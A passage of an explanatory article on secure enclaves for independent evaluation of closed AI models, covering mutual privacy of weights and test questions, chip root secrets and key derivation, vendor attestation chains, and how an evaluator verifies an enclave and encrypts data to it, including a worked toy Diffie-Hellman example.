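# Secure enclaves for outside access to closed AI models

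## Why outsiders need access to closed models, and what a secure enclave offers

A secure enclave, also known as a trusted execution environment, is a protected area of a computer chip. The chip encrypts everything the enclave holds in memory and can prove to a remote party which software the enclave is running. Chipmakers designed enclaves for people who rent computers from a company they would rather not trust with their data. Since 2024, AI researchers have also been experimenting with enclaves as a way for outsiders to test an AI model that its owner keeps secret, while keeping their own information secret too.

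A closed model is one whose owner does not release its weights, the numbers the model learns in training. Anyone who has the weights and the code to run them can run the model. Everyone else uses a closed model through a chat product or an application programming interface (API), which lets a customer's program send text to the owner's servers and get text back. The strongest models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google are all closed.

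The owners of closed models test them and see far more of the system than any outsider does. *Developing a Framework for Secure Third-Party Access to Frontier AI* (Hurel, Glantz and Cuthbert, 2026) argues that owners also work fast and under commercial pressure, which leaves blind spots. The Royal United Services Institute, a London defence think tank, published the report with Google's support. An outside evaluator may want to know whether a model can help someone automate a cyberattack, or whether its safeguards hold against a determined user. The UK's AI Security Institute assessed 30 models between 2023 and 2025. The EU's code of practice for general-purpose AI commits its signatories to giving independent evaluators "sufficient access", though nobody has settled how much that is.

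Evaluators can have different degrees of access to a model. With black-box access, they submit questions and read the answers. Grey-box access adds some information about the model's internals, such as the probability it gives to each possible next word. White-box access includes the model's weights, architecture and internal activity as it runs. Deeper access allows more thorough testing but also exposes more of the model to theft.

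### What each side wants to hide

One way to test a closed model is to send it questions through the owner's API, but the questions then arrive on the owner's servers in plain text, as Trask, Messing and colleagues (2026) point out in *Double Blind Evals*. Another is for the owner to hand over the weights, but Trask, Messing and colleagues know of no case in which an outside evaluator got a readable copy of a frontier model's weights in order to keep a test secret. In *Piloting the world's first double-blind AI evaluations*, which announced an enclave trial with a Gemini model, Google's Isaac, Messing and Lum (2026) also describe a choice between the evaluator giving up the questions and the owner giving up the weights.

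Owners usually cite intellectual property to explain their reluctance, but patents and copyright give model weights little protection, at least in the United States. According to the US chapter of Chambers' *AI & Intellectual Property 2026* (2026), by the law firm Sidley Austin, copyright is unlikely to cover weights because they come out of a training process and have no human author, and bare numbers fall outside the categories of patent law. As of mid-2026, no US court had squarely recognised copyright in weights. Copyright can protect human-written code, but not a model's overall design, which counts as an idea. An owner may, however, be able to patent a system that embodies that design.

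That leaves contracts and trade secrets. Information qualifies as a trade secret only if it has economic value because others do not know it and cannot readily find it out, and if its owner takes reasonable measures to keep it secret. An owner whose weights end up on the public internet may well lose this protection. Even while the protection lasts, the owner has no claim against a rival who reaches the same result independently or by reverse engineering.

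The weights are the most valuable item. Bucknall, Trager and Osborne (2025), in *Ensuring mutual privacy is necessary for effective external evaluation*, put the training cost of the most advanced commercial models at tens of millions of dollars. The architecture, meaning the number, size and type of the model's layers, is a separate secret, because a better design achieves the same performance with less computing. They cite an estimate that such algorithmic improvements halve the computing needed for a given performance about every eight months. The inference code, which runs the finished model to produce its answers, can also contain tricks that competitors would like to have.

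Google DeepMind's *An Approach to Technical AGI Safety and Security* (2025) gives two reasons for guarding model weights: preventing misuse and protecting intellectual property. Someone who has the weights can retrain the model to remove its safeguards, and the owner cannot recall a copied file. In 2023, Meta gave its LLaMA model to approved outside researchers, and the whole model, including its weights, ended up on the file-sharing network BitTorrent. Hurel and colleagues classify the leak as accidental exposure, which requires no adversary.

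Evaluators mainly need to keep the test itself secret, because a model that has seen the questions in training can score well from memory, a problem known as contamination. Schaeffer, Kazdan and colleagues (2026), in *Quantifying the Effect of Test Set Contamination on Generative Evaluations*, measured the effect by pretraining dozens of language models on text mixed with varying numbers of copies of a mathematics test. Scores rose with the number of copies, sharply at around 100, and larger models gained more from the same exposure. One carelessly handled log file would contribute far fewer than 100 copies, so the experiment is better evidence about deliberate or repeated exposure than about a single slip. Still, leaks seem to be common. *Double Blind Evals* cites a 2024 study by Xu and colleagues that found strong signs of leaked test material in the training of roughly half of 31 models.

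The team that runs ARC-AGI, a benchmark of abstract reasoning, already acts on this worry by keeping one set of problems off commercial APIs altogether. It uses a separate "semi-private" set for models available only through an API. OpenAI's o3 was tested on the semi-private set but not on the fully private one.

Some test questions are also dangerous themselves. A serious test of whether a model can help with a pathogen or break into a network may have to contain the kind of knowledge it tests for, and a government that writes such a test will not want it stored on a company's servers.

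Evaluators may also want to hide their methods. Bucknall and colleagues draw a parallel with the Volkswagen emissions scandal. Volkswagen's software detected official tests from the steering wheel's position, the speed, the engine's running time and the air pressure, and adjusted the emission controls accordingly. This was possible because the test procedure was public. An AI company would not need detection software, since it generally knows when a test is taking place and runs the model on its own machines.

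### Structured access and structured transparency

Much of the vocabulary for this problem comes from two older ideas. The first is structured access, which Shevlane (2022) proposed in *Structured Access* as a middle course between publishing a model and withholding it. The developer keeps the model and lets people use it through an interface. This is meant to prevent harmful use, and to stop people from getting around restrictions on use by modifying the model or reverse engineering a copy. Shevlane compares it to a keycard that opens only certain rooms in a building.

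The reasoning behind offering access through an interface is that software is both information and a tool. A developer who can only choose which information to publish can't allow the good uses without also allowing the bad ones. Microsoft researchers once released a chatbot, DialoGPT, without the last piece of code needed to make it produce text, because its output was often offensive. Users could do nothing with it unless they found a substitute for the missing code online, and then they could use it without restriction. An interface avoids this problem by letting the developer vet users, monitor what they ask, and withdraw a capability that turns out badly.

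In outside testing, structured access protects the developer's model weights but not the researcher's privacy. Shevlane suggests, for instance, that a researcher could upload a tool for analysing a model's internals, which the developer would run before sending back the results. The developer would then have the researcher's tool, and the scheme also relies partly on monitoring. Shevlane raises users' privacy as a matter for further work. The chapter also addresses the objection that structured access concentrates power in developers' hands. This objection is especially strong for outside testing, because the company being examined would set the terms of the examination. Shevlane answers that governments or independent bodies could set the rules, including a minimum level of access for outside researchers.

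Structured transparency governs what a person can learn. It is a broader idea than structured access, which governs what a person can do with a model. *Beyond Privacy Trade-offs with Structured Transparency* (Trask, Bluemke et al., 2020) uses the term for any system that enforces standards, fixed in advance, about who may know what, when they may know it and what they may do with it. For example, a bomb-sniffing dog reveals whether a bag contains explosives and nothing else about the contents.

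They break the aim into five components and illustrate each with the example of a mailed letter. Bluemke, Collins and colleagues later applied the same five components to outside scrutiny of AI models in *Exploring the Relevance of Data Privacy-Enhancing Technologies for AI Governance Use Cases*.

| Component | In a letter | In a test of a closed model |
|---|---|---|
| Input privacy | The envelope | The evaluator runs agreed computations on the model without getting a copy |
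| Output privacy | Leaving sensitive details out of the text | Nobody can reconstruct the model from the results |
| Input verification | The signature | The owner proves which version of the model took the test |
| Output verification | The wax seal | The evaluator can check that the test code ran unaltered |
| Flow governance | A safe whose combination only the recipient knows | The test runs only when the agreed parties approve |

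These are hard to achieve together mainly because of what Trask and colleagues call the copy problem, which is that whoever receives information can do as they like with it afterwards. The traditional remedy is a trusted third party who sees everything and reports only what each side may know. But this third party is even better informed, and somebody has to watch them too, which is known as the recursive oversight problem. An enclave is an attempt to replace the trusted third party with a machine. The 2020 scheme lists enclaves among the tools for input privacy, which fairly reflects their limits. An enclave can hide the inputs, but the agreed results still come out and may reveal something about them.

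### The case for privacy on both sides

Bucknall and colleagues define this standoff formally. P_M is the set of things the model owner wants to keep from the evaluator, and R_E is the set of things the evaluator requires from the owner. If the two sets overlap (P_M ∩ R_E ≠ ∅), there is a privacy problem. Similarly, P_E is what the evaluator wants to keep from the owner, and R_M is what the owner requires from the evaluator. If these sets also overlap (P_E ∩ R_M ≠ ∅), the two sides have a mutual privacy problem.

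The first overlap includes weights, internal activity and training data. The second includes the evaluator's questions, even though the model owner has no real need to read them. The owner needs assurance that the evaluator is staying within the agreed bounds and protecting any confidential material. Watching the evaluation is the natural way to get that assurance, but it exposes the questions. This is encouraging for a technical fix, because an owner who could get the assurance another way would lose most of its reason for demanding to see the test.

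They argue that outside evaluation cannot be effective until both sides have privacy, and that existing practice protects only the owner. Even with contracts and zero-logging promises, evaluators who work through the owner's API have to trust that nobody keeps a log. Many of the technical proposals they survey also favor the owner, either requiring the owner to approve all the audit code or assuming that the owner sees the whole audit. They attribute this partly to bargaining power, since outside evaluations rest on voluntary agreements and an owner who dislikes the terms can refuse to take part. A badly drafted legal duty could instead favor the evaluator too much and leave the model insecure.

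The position paper addresses two serious objections. The first is that nobody can judge the quality of test questions that are kept secret. The paper replies that an accreditation body could vet evaluators, and that secrecy could vary with the sensitivity of the material. The second objection is that owners know their models best and could help. After an audit by the evaluator now called METR, Anthropic staff wrote that they could have helped it find more concerning behaviour had they known more about its methods. Bucknall and colleagues answer that deeper access would give the evaluator much of the same benefit, though it would have to rediscover some things the owner already knew. But deeper access is what owners are most reluctant to give, which weakens this answer.

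The word "necessary" in the paper's title is probably too strong for every kind of test. Someone who improvises attacks on a chatbot loses less if the prompts are logged than someone with a fixed set of 500 questions that took a year to write. The argument seems right for the fixed set, and official bodies have begun to act on it. NIST, the US standards agency, is working with OpenMined, a developer of privacy software, on evaluations that meet the security needs of both AI developers and the owners of the test data.

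### The cryptography behind an enclave

An enclave depends on a few standard cryptographic tools. A key is a long number that a computer uses to scramble or unscramble data. A symmetric key does both. Symmetric encryption is fast, which matters when a file of model weights is hundreds of gigabytes in size. But both sides need the same key, and anyone who intercepts it on the way can read everything encrypted with it.

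Public-key cryptography avoids this problem with two related numbers, a public key and a private key. The holder publishes the public key and keeps the private key secret. Anyone can encrypt a message with the public key, but only the private key can decrypt it. Public-key operations are slow on large files, so in practice two parties use them to agree on a new symmetric key, then encrypt the bulk of the data with that key.

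A hash is a short fingerprint of a file. The widely used function SHA-256 turns any input, from a sentence to an operating system, into a string of 256 bits. The same file always gives the same string, changing one character gives a completely different string, and nobody knows a practical way to construct two files with the same hash. Two people can therefore check that they have identical software by comparing hashes. The hash of the software in an enclave is called a measurement.

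To sign a message, the holder of a private key computes the message's hash and combines it with the key to produce a signature. Anyone with the matching public key can check that the signature fits the message. A valid signature shows that the message came from the holder of that private key and that nobody has altered it since, but it does not keep the message secret.

Suppose an evaluator receives a public key and a claim that it belongs to a genuine Intel chip. A fraudster could generate a key pair and make the same claim, so the evaluator needs a certificate, which is a statement that the key belongs to the chip, signed by someone the evaluator already trusts. For enclaves, the chip's manufacturer signs the certificate. The evaluator must still get the manufacturer's public key from a reliable source and trust the manufacturer to be careful about what it signs.

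### The simple picture, and the three parties

In the simplest picture of an enclave, a chip holds a private key that never leaves it, and the manufacturer vouches for the matching public key. The model owner uses that public key to encrypt the weights, and the evaluator uses it to encrypt the questions. Both send their encrypted files to the machine, whose operator can copy them but cannot read them. Inside the enclave, the chip decrypts the files, runs the questions through the model and releases the result the two sides agreed on.

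Real enclaves use several keys. If outsiders encrypted their data directly to one permanent key, nothing would tie the data to a particular program. Somebody could load different software onto the same genuine chip, decrypt the files and send them anywhere. In the design that *Double Blind Evals* describes, the chip derives one key from a secret that the manufacturer put there and uses it to sign a statement of what software is running. The enclave also makes a temporary key pair at start-up to protect the data that outsiders send in. Another temporary key encrypts the memory.

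Evaluating a closed model in an enclave involves three parties. The model owner supplies the weights and inference code, and the evaluator supplies the questions and often some code for scoring the answers. The host, usually a cloud company, runs the computer that contains the enclave. On an ordinary rented computer, a dishonest host could read everything its customers put there, or run a different program from the one they requested and send back invented results. An enclave is meant to prevent both unless the host and the chip's manufacturer collude.

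Protecting data from the host does not by itself protect the owner and the evaluator from each other. For that, both must know and accept what the software in the enclave will do with their data before they send any.

*Secure Enclaves for AI Evaluation*, a paper by Trask, Yesilyurt and colleagues on a small 2024 pilot, notes that the model owner, the evaluator or an outside cloud company can host the enclave, because its protection is not supposed to depend on the host's good faith. In the 2026 Gemini trial, Google both owned the model and ran the cloud, so the encryption had to hide the evaluators' questions from Google even while they were in its data centre.

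## The secret burned into the chip and the keys derived from it

Everything an outsider can check remotely about an enclave depends on a secret number inside the chip. This root secret is different in every chip, and the chip uses it to compute the keys that prove its identity. Intel, AMD and NVIDIA all use this approach, but they differ in what they compute from the secret and in what role a copy of it plays in their own systems.

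### How the secret gets into the chip

A factory makes many copies of the same circuit, so the manufacturer has to add something afterwards to make each chip unique. The usual method is to set fuses, microscopic elements that a pulse of current changes permanently. Each fuse stores one bit, so 256 of them can hold a 256-bit number, which survives when the power goes off.

*Supporting Intel® SGX on Multi-Package Platforms* (Johnson, Makaram and colleagues, 2025) describes two root secrets in each Intel processor. The Provisioning Root Key lets the chip prove its identity to outsiders, and the Sealing Root Key protects data that an enclave stores for later use. In a support article, Intel says that it generates the Sealing Root Keys at random, burns them into the fuses and then removes all traces of them from its systems. Outsiders cannot confirm this. Intel does keep a copy of each Provisioning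 Root Key so that it can vouch for the chip. It stores the copy in a hardware security module, a tamper-resistant device for storing keys, according to heise online's *Intel encryption technology SGX*.

Ordinary software cannot read a root secret because the chip's designers give it no path to the fuses. On an Intel processor, a program inside an enclave can run an instruction that returns a key computed from the secret, but no instruction returns the secret itself. AMD and NVIDIA handle keys on a small separate processor that runs only firmware (the low-level software that operates the hardware) signed by the manufacturer. These protections depend on good engineering and can fail. A researcher has read the Provisioning Root Key out of an old line of Intel's low-cost Celeron processors.

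### A different key for each firmware version

Firmware has bugs, and some of them let an attacker into the enclave. If a chip signed everything with one permanent key, its signature would look the same before and after a repair. Manufacturers avoid this by making the firmware version part of the key:

key = KDF(root secret, firmware version)

A key derivation function (KDF) is like a hash in that changing either input gives a completely different key, and nobody can work backwards from the key to the root secret.

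Suppose a chip with root secret S runs firmware version 7, so its signing key is K7 = KDF(S, 7). Researchers then find a flaw in version 7 that lets a dishonest host steal this key. The manufacturer fixes the flaw in version 8, and once the host installs the update, the chip computes K8 = KDF(S, 8). The manufacturer also issues a certificate for K8 that contains the version number. An evaluator can then require version 8 or later and reject any signature made with K7. A thief who has K7 can still sign with it, but those signatures match only the certificate for version 7, and the thief can't compute K8 without S. A host that secretly stays on version 7 also can't produce a signature the evaluator will accept.

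The evaluator has to set the minimum because the certificate for K7 doesn't expire when version 8 comes out. Intel's and AMD's certificates for these keys last about seven years, and a verifier that checked only the signatures would accept the old key throughout.

Newer firmware can usually compute the older keys. AMD's *SEV Secure Nested Paging Firmware ABI Specification* (2025) allows a chip to compute its key for any version up to the current one, so that it can carry over secrets from before an update. A chain of hashes is one way to give newer firmware the older keys without giving older firmware the newer ones. The chip computes a key for the highest version number the scheme allows, say 127. Hashing that key gives the key for version 126, hashing again gives 125, and so on. At start-up, the chip goes down the chain to the current version and hides the keys for later versions. Version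 8 can then hash its key to get version 7's, but version 7 would have to reverse a hash to get version 8's. AMD calls the key material it sends to cloud companies a "hashstick", which suggests that AMD uses this construction.

Intel's *Trusted Computing Base Recovery Attestation* describes the process Intel starts when a flaw calls for new firmware. Everyone concerned installs the update, and verifiers can then tell updated machines from the rest. The trusted computing base is all the hardware, firmware and software that must behave correctly for the protection to hold. Versioning only helps with the parts of it that can change. Intel's technical notes on attestation, the procedure by which an enclave proves what it is, describe the processor's logic as immutable, so a flaw there may remain for the life of the chip.

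### Intel's chain of keys

Intel has two enclave technologies. The older one, SGX, encloses a single program. TDX encloses a whole virtual computer, known as a confidential virtual machine, and is the one that works with NVIDIA's GPUs. Chuang, Seto and colleagues point out in *TEE.fail* that both depend on the same signing key for attestation.

That key is the Provisioning Certification Key, or PCK. The processor derives it from the fused Provisioning Root Key and the versions of the trusted components. Intel repeats the calculation with its own copy of the root key and issues a certificate for the public half of the result. This certificate includes separate version numbers for 16 components (Intel, 2020). An intermediate certificate authority signs it, and Intel's root authority signs the intermediate authority's certificate.

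Only the Provisioning Certification Enclave, a small enclave written by Intel, may use the PCK. It uses the PCK to certify an attestation key, not to sign statements about a customer's enclave. Another Intel program, the quoting enclave, creates the attestation key and uses it to sign the report on what software is running. Intel calls the signed report a quote. A verifier follows the signatures from the quote to the attestation key, then to the PCK, the intermediate authority and Intel's root.

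On a server with more than one processor, a program may move between processors and must find the same keys on each, but Intel did not want any processor's fused secrets to leave that chip. Johnson and colleagues explain that the processors instead agree on new, random platform root keys when someone sets up the server, possibly in the customer's own data centre. The secret behind the attestation therefore does not come from the factory, and the fused keys only protect it. Each processor encrypts a copy of the root keys with its own hardware key and saves it in flash memory. The server also sends Intel's registration service a copy of the platform's provisioning key, with an authenticated list of the processors that share it. If the service approves the registration, it derives the PCK and issues the certificate.

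Under one policy of its registration service, Intel discards its copy of these platform keys as soon as it has derived the PCK, and a flag in the certificate shows that Intel hasn't kept them.

To revoke a bad chip, Intel adds the chip's certificate to a published list. Intel keeps separate lists for the root authority, the intermediate authority that covers single processors, and the authority that covers multi-processor servers. Cloud companies often download certificates in bulk and serve them from a local store so that machines don't have to contact Intel every time they start, but stored revocation lists can become outdated. In November 2025, after the TEE.fail researchers had built a bot that produced fake quotes with a genuine key, Intel updated its lists and warned that the checking tool supplied with the bot would still accept the fakes because it used an old copy of the lists.

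### AMD's versioned chip key

In SEV-SNP, AMD's technology for confidential virtual machines, a separate security processor manages the keys, and the main processor's operating system cannot access them directly. The chip's secrets are stored in fuses that AMD can write only once, according to Morphisms' *Cryptographic Keys*, an online guide. The chip derives its Versioned Chip Endorsement Key (VCEK) from these secrets. The VCEK signs attestation reports directly, without an additional key like the one Intel's quoting enclave uses.

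The "version" in this key is a set of numbers. On the processors AMD code-named Milan and Genoa, the set has four, one each for the microcode (the processor's own internal instructions), the SEV-SNP firmware, the security processor's operating system and its boot loader. The later Turin design adds a fifth for another piece of firmware.

A cloud operator can try out new firmware before committing to it. In AMD's example, a machine running version 1.51.1 provisionally loads 1.51.21. Until the operator commits, the chip signs with a key no newer than the one for the committed version, and the only other firmware it will accept is 1.51.1. The operator can also keep using an older version's key for a while after an update, so that customers have time to fetch the new certificate. A signature can therefore make the firmware look older than it is, which doesn't harm the customer, but it can't make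 the firmware look newer. The operator can also switch off signing with the chip key, which blocks attestation but doesn't fake it, because the report then has zeroes in place of the signature.

AMD's *Versioned Chip Endorsement Key (VCEK) Certificate and KDS Interface Specification* (2025) sets out a chain of three certificates. The AMD Root Key signs the certificate of an intermediate key, the AMD SEV Key, which signs the chip's certificate. AMD creates chip certificates on request and doesn't store them. It also issues certificates for firmware versions that don't exist yet, so operators can have them ready. To do this, AMD must be able to compute the public half of a key that no chip has yet produced, so it must hold the chip's secret or something equivalent.

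AMD's revocation lists offer no obvious way to revoke a single chip. The lists, one for each product line, identify certificates by serial number, and AMD gives every chip certificate the serial number zero. AMD can use a list to revoke an intermediate key, but doing so revokes the whole product line. An evaluator who knows that a chip is bad can still reject it using the hardware identifier in its certificate.

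AMD also offers cloud companies another signing key, the Versioned Loaded Endorsement Key (VLEK). AMD keeps the seeds for these keys on its own servers rather than in the chip's fuses, with dedicated seeds for each cloud company. It derives the key material for a given firmware version and encrypts it so that one particular chip can decrypt it. The cloud company then loads it onto that chip. AMD's *Versioned Loaded Endorsement Key (VLEK) Certificate Definition* (2023) gives these keys a separate intermediate certificate authority. The host can require a virtual machine to use the VLEK instead of the chip's own key.

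A VLEK signature helps an evaluator by tying the machine to a particular cloud company, which an attacker with an AMD server at home could not imitate. But the key depends on the company's seed and the firmware version, and apparently not on the chip, so an attacker could use one stolen VLEK to impersonate many machines.

### NVIDIA's device key and its five certificates

Large models run on GPUs, and the H100 was NVIDIA's first to offer full enclave protection. NVIDIA has published only outlines of how this works. In *Blueprint, Bootstrap, and Bridge*, Gu, Valdez and colleagues (2026) reconstructed much of it by intercepting traffic between the software and the GPU and comparing it with NVIDIA's patents and the open parts of its driver.

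The secret fused into an NVIDIA GPU is the Device Identity Key. Only SEC2, a security processor inside the GPU, appears to have access to it. At start-up, the GPU combines this secret with measurements of its firmware to derive an attestation key pair. The measurements depend on the firmware itself, unlike the version numbers from which AMD derives its chip key. Changing one byte of an NVIDIA GPU's firmware should therefore change the attestation key, even if the version number stays the same.

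Five certificates connect the attestation key to NVIDIA:

| Certificate | What it vouches for | Where the verifier gets it |
|---|---|---|
| Attestation | The key that signs this GPU's reports | The GPU, which signs it with the Device Identity Key |
| Device Identity | The key fused into this GPU | The GPU |
| Provisioner | The NVIDIA authority that signs device certificates | The driver |
| Model | The authority for the GPU model | The driver |
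| Root | NVIDIA itself | The driver, but the verifier substitutes its own copy |

The verifier brings its own root certificate because a tampered driver could supply a false one with false certificates to match.

To check for revocation, the verifier queries an online NVIDIA service about whether each certificate is still good. NVIDIA's *API Documentation* describes the answers as real-time. This avoids the problem Intel had with stale lists, but makes every check depend on a service that NVIDIA runs. Verifying a GPU locally doesn't remove the dependence, because a local verifier still gets the certificate status and the reference values for the firmware from NVIDIA, as Intel notes in the documentation for its own attestation service.

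NVIDIA needs only the public half of a Device Identity Key to certify it. Intel and AMD need a secret from which they can derive the chip's private key, because they issue certificates for later firmware versions without receiving any more data from the chip. NVIDIA's arrangement is therefore safer in principle, though a customer still has to trust that nobody at the factory kept a copy of the private half.

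A GPU enclave has to work with a confidential virtual machine on an Intel or AMD processor, which starts the GPU's protection and checks its certificates. Anyone who sends weights or test questions to such a machine is trusting both the GPU's manufacturer and the processor's, and a failure at the processor's manufacturer also undermines the GPU's protection.

### Four keys that popular accounts merge

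Where popular accounts have a single burned-in key, the systems described above have at least four.

| Key | Where it comes from | How long it lasts | What it does |
|---|---|---|---|
| Root secret | Factory-set fuses, or random generation during set-up on multi-processor Intel servers | The life of the chip or platform set-up | Provides the starting point for the identity keys |
| Attestation signing key | Derivation from the root secret and firmware, with a further certified key at Intel | Usually until the firmware changes | Signs reports of what is running |
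| Memory-encryption key | The processor, which makes a new one for each confidential virtual machine | Until the virtual machine stops | Encrypts what the enclave holds in memory |
| Session key pair | Software inside the enclave, at start-up | Until the enclave stops | Lets outsiders send data that only the enclave can read |

Outsiders cannot encrypt to Intel's or AMD's attestation keys because both companies use ECDSA, a signature algorithm with no encryption step. In the design that Trask and colleagues used, the enclave creates a fresh session key pair and puts the public half in the report that the attestation key signs. Outsiders can then check the signature and encrypt to the session key. Intel also provides for this approach, and its *Infrastructure Setup* lists a public key among the data that a verifier may expect to find in a TDX quote.

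The choice of encryption key matters a great deal if a chip's root secret later leaks. Suppose an eavesdropper records a model's encrypted weights on their way to the enclave, and somebody extracts the secret two years later. If the owner encrypted the weights to a key derived from that secret, the eavesdropper can now decrypt the recording. If the owner used a fresh session key that disappeared when the enclave shut down, the recording remains useless, although the thief can pose as the chip from then on.

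The link between processor and GPU also uses fresh keys. *NVIDIA Secure AI with Blackwell and Hopper GPUs* (Nertney and Mandakolathur, 2025) describes a Diffie-Hellman exchange, which lets two parties agree on a secret over a line that others can read. The exchange gives the driver in the virtual machine and the firmware in the GPU the same symmetric key. The system destroys its temporary keys when the virtual machine shuts down or the GPU resets.

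### If the manufacturer cheats or a key escapes

The manufacturer is the root of trust, because every chain of certificates ends with a key that it controls. A dishonest manufacturer could fake an enclave without a chip by creating a key pair on a laptop, signing a certificate that says the key belongs to a genuine enclave, and collecting whatever outsiders send. Intel and AMD can also compute the signing keys of real chips, so they could imitate an existing machine without issuing a new certificate that might raise suspicion.

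To exploit this, the manufacturer would also have to get between the outsider and the real machine, most easily by colluding with the host. Some outsiders may think collusion more likely than others do. Intel, AMD, NVIDIA and the largest Western cloud companies are all American, so a foreign government with secret test questions might worry that one legal order could apply to both the chipmaker and the host.

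A manufacturer could also sign firmware with a back door. Trask and colleagues note that the closed firmware at the bottom of the system is the same for every customer, so a cloud operator cannot alter it to target one of them. But the manufacturer could still sign a special image for one machine. AMD's chip key depends on version numbers, so an image that reused the public version's numbers would produce the same key. NVIDIA's use of measurements would expose the change, unless NVIDIA also published a matching false reference value.

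A copy of the provisioning secret would not by itself let a manufacturer read memory or decrypt old traffic, because the memory and session keys are temporary and separate. The manufacturer would have to act while a test was being set up or running.

A key stolen from one chip endangers more than that chip's owner. Chuang and colleagues used one stolen PCK to sign false SGX and TDX reports on machines with no protection. An evaluator who accepts any genuine, up-to-date Intel processor would have accepted these reports. If the thief has only the signing key for one firmware version, updating the firmware and raising the minimum accepted version will block that key. But a thief with the root secret can compute the key for each new version, so updates don't help and verifiers have to block the chip itself.

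Blocking chips does not help if someone steals one of the manufacturer's certification keys, because the thief can then invent as many chips as needed, each with a new identifier. The manufacturer would have to revoke the stolen key, which would also invalidate the certificates of all the genuine chips below it, and then issue new certificates. AMD limits the damage by giving most product lines their own root key. Intel's SGX hierarchy has a single root certificate, valid until the end of 2049. Intel could use the root to revoke a stolen intermediate key, but if the root key itself were stolen, no higher authority could revoke it, and everyone who relies on the root certificate would have to replace their stored copy.

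## How an outsider checks an enclave and encrypts data to it

Suppose an evaluator wants to send a file of 500 secret test questions to an enclave in a data centre. The evaluator has never seen the machine and has to assume that the host will read whatever it can. Before sending the file, the evaluator therefore needs evidence that a genuine chip is running the agreed software, and a key for encrypting the file so that only this software can decrypt it. One signed report from the chip can provide both, as long as the protocol around it has no gaps.

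### Measuring each layer as it starts

A confidential virtual machine starts in layers, like an ordinary computer. Firmware loads the kernel, the core of the operating system. The kernel starts background services, and these start the application. In an enclave, each layer hashes the next one before handing over control, because a program that hashed itself could report a false hash. By the time a tampered kernel runs, the firmware has already recorded the kernel's hash, and the kernel can't change that record.

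The record often takes the form of a hardware register that software can add to but not overwrite. Each new layer updates it like this:

m_new = H(m_old ‖ H(next layer))

H is the hash function, and ‖ joins two strings end to end. Changing any layer, or the order in which the layers load, changes the final value.

Meta's *Private Processing for WhatsApp* (2025) describes these checks in a service that summarises users' messages inside enclaves. AMD's security processor hashes the virtual machine's firmware, kernel, kernel start-up options and small initial file system. The initial file system contains the expected hash of the main file system and checks that the main file system matches before using it, so the processor's hash covers both. A program in the main file system then checks the application. The virtual machine also compares the GPU's report with reference values from NVIDIA, and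 shuts down if they don't match.

All these layers belong to the trusted computing base, so designers remove whatever they can. Meta removed the network interfaces and all non-essential services from the operating system, so data enters and leaves through a few controlled channels. Designers also have to remove remote login. Trask and colleagues point out that an administrator who could log in after the chip had signed the hash could change the code, and the evaluator would still be relying on the old hash.

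### What the chip signs

The laptop opens the exchange by sending a nonce, a random number that it will use only once. The software in the enclave has its session key pair, with a private key a and a public key A. WhatsApp's enclaves make a new pair for every connection and not just at start-up. The software passes the nonce and a hash of A to the chip. The chip adds the measurement and the firmware versions, and signs everything with its attestation key k:

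R = (m, N, H(A), v)

σ = Sign(k, R)

The enclave sends the laptop the report R, the signature σ, the public key A and the certificates that connect the attestation key to the manufacturer.

| Item in the report | Where it comes from | What the laptop compares it with |
|---|---|---|
| m, the measurement | The chip and the start-up layers | The hash of the software the evaluator has agreed to |
| N, the nonce | The laptop, by way of the enclave's software | The number it sent a moment ago |
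| H(A), the hash of the session public key | The enclave's software | A hash that the laptop computes from the key it received |
| v, the firmware versions | The chip | The evaluator's minimum, and the versions in the signing key's certificate |

Real formats differ a little. WhatsApp's enclaves put the nonce into a larger bundle of evidence, and the signed report contains a hash of the bundle.

The chip copies the nonce and the hash of the key from a field that the software fills in, without interpreting them. A malicious program on a genuine chip could put the hash of anybody's key there, but that program would have a different measurement. The measurement identifies the software that supplied the key, so the evaluator can trust the key only after checking the measurement.

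The laptop first follows the certificates from the signature up to the manufacturer's root key, using its own stored copy of that root, and checks for revoked certificates. It then makes the four comparisons in the table. It should also check that the enclave isn't in debug mode, a developer setting that lets the host look inside. If any check fails, the laptop sends nothing.

### Agreeing on a key and encrypting the file

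The laptop and the enclave can now agree on a symmetric key by Diffie-Hellman exchange. You can do the whole calculation by hand with toy numbers. Both sides use the public prime p = 23 and the public base g = 5. "Mod 23" means the remainder after dividing by 23.

The enclave's private key is a = 6, so its public key is

A = 5^6 mod 23 = 15,625 mod 23 = 8

The laptop has already found H(8) in the signed report. It picks its own private number, b = 15, and computes

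B = 5^15 mod 23 = 19

It sends 19 to the enclave. Each side then raises the other's public number to the power of its own private number:

Laptop: 8^15 mod 23 = 2

Enclave: 19^6 mod 23 = 2

The results agree because both equal 5^(6 × 15) mod 23. An eavesdropper has seen 23, 5, 8 and 19, but needs either 6 or 15 to calculate the shared result, 2. With a prime this small, trying every possibility takes a minute. Real systems use primes of at least 2,048 bits, or an equivalent calculation on an elliptic curve with numbers of about 256 bits. No existing computer can search that many possibilities.

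The shared value doesn't serve as the encryption key directly. Both sides put it through a key derivation function, together with the nonce and the two public numbers, which ties the key to this particular exchange. The laptop then encrypts the file:

K = KDF(2, N, A, B)

C = Enc(K, file)

It sends C to the enclave, which derives the same K and decrypts the file inside its protected memory. The usual encryption methods also add a tag to C that lets the enclave detect any alteration. The host can copy C and see its size, but it can't read the questions without K.

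To return the results, the enclave derives a second key, K′, from the shared value and sends Enc(K′, results), which only the laptop can decrypt. If the agreed software also gives results to the model owner, it encrypts that copy with a key from the owner's own session.

Services that use TLS, the protocol behind secure websites, add a step. The key in the chip's report signs the handshake, the opening messages in which the two sides exchange new Diffie-Hellman numbers. The evaluator still relies on the report to tie the connection to the measured software.

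### Without a nonce, an old report still works

Now suppose the protocol has no nonce. On Monday, a dishonest host extracts the session private key from a running enclave and keeps it with the enclave's signed report. On Friday, the evaluator connects, and the host sends Monday's report. The signature is valid, the measurement is correct, and the hash matches the public key, so the evaluator encrypts the 500 questions to that key. The host can then decrypt them with the stolen private key.

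Replaying an old report only helps someone who has the private key that goes with it. An attacker who steals that key in one break-in can keep exploiting the break-in indefinitely by replaying the report, without further access to the enclave or its data centre.

WhatsApp's system lacked a freshness check before its launch. The security firm Trail of Bits audited the system and rated this flaw as high severity. According to its *What we learned about TEE security from auditing WhatsApp's Private Inference* (2026), an attacker who had compromised one enclave could have run a fake server anywhere, and WhatsApp clients would have trusted it. Meta fixed the flaw by putting a random number from the client's opening message into every report.

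With the nonce, the laptop rejects Monday's report because it contains the wrong number. The thief can't get a new report for the stolen key either, since the measured software gives the chip only the hash of a key that the software made itself.

### Without a bound session key, someone can sit in the middle

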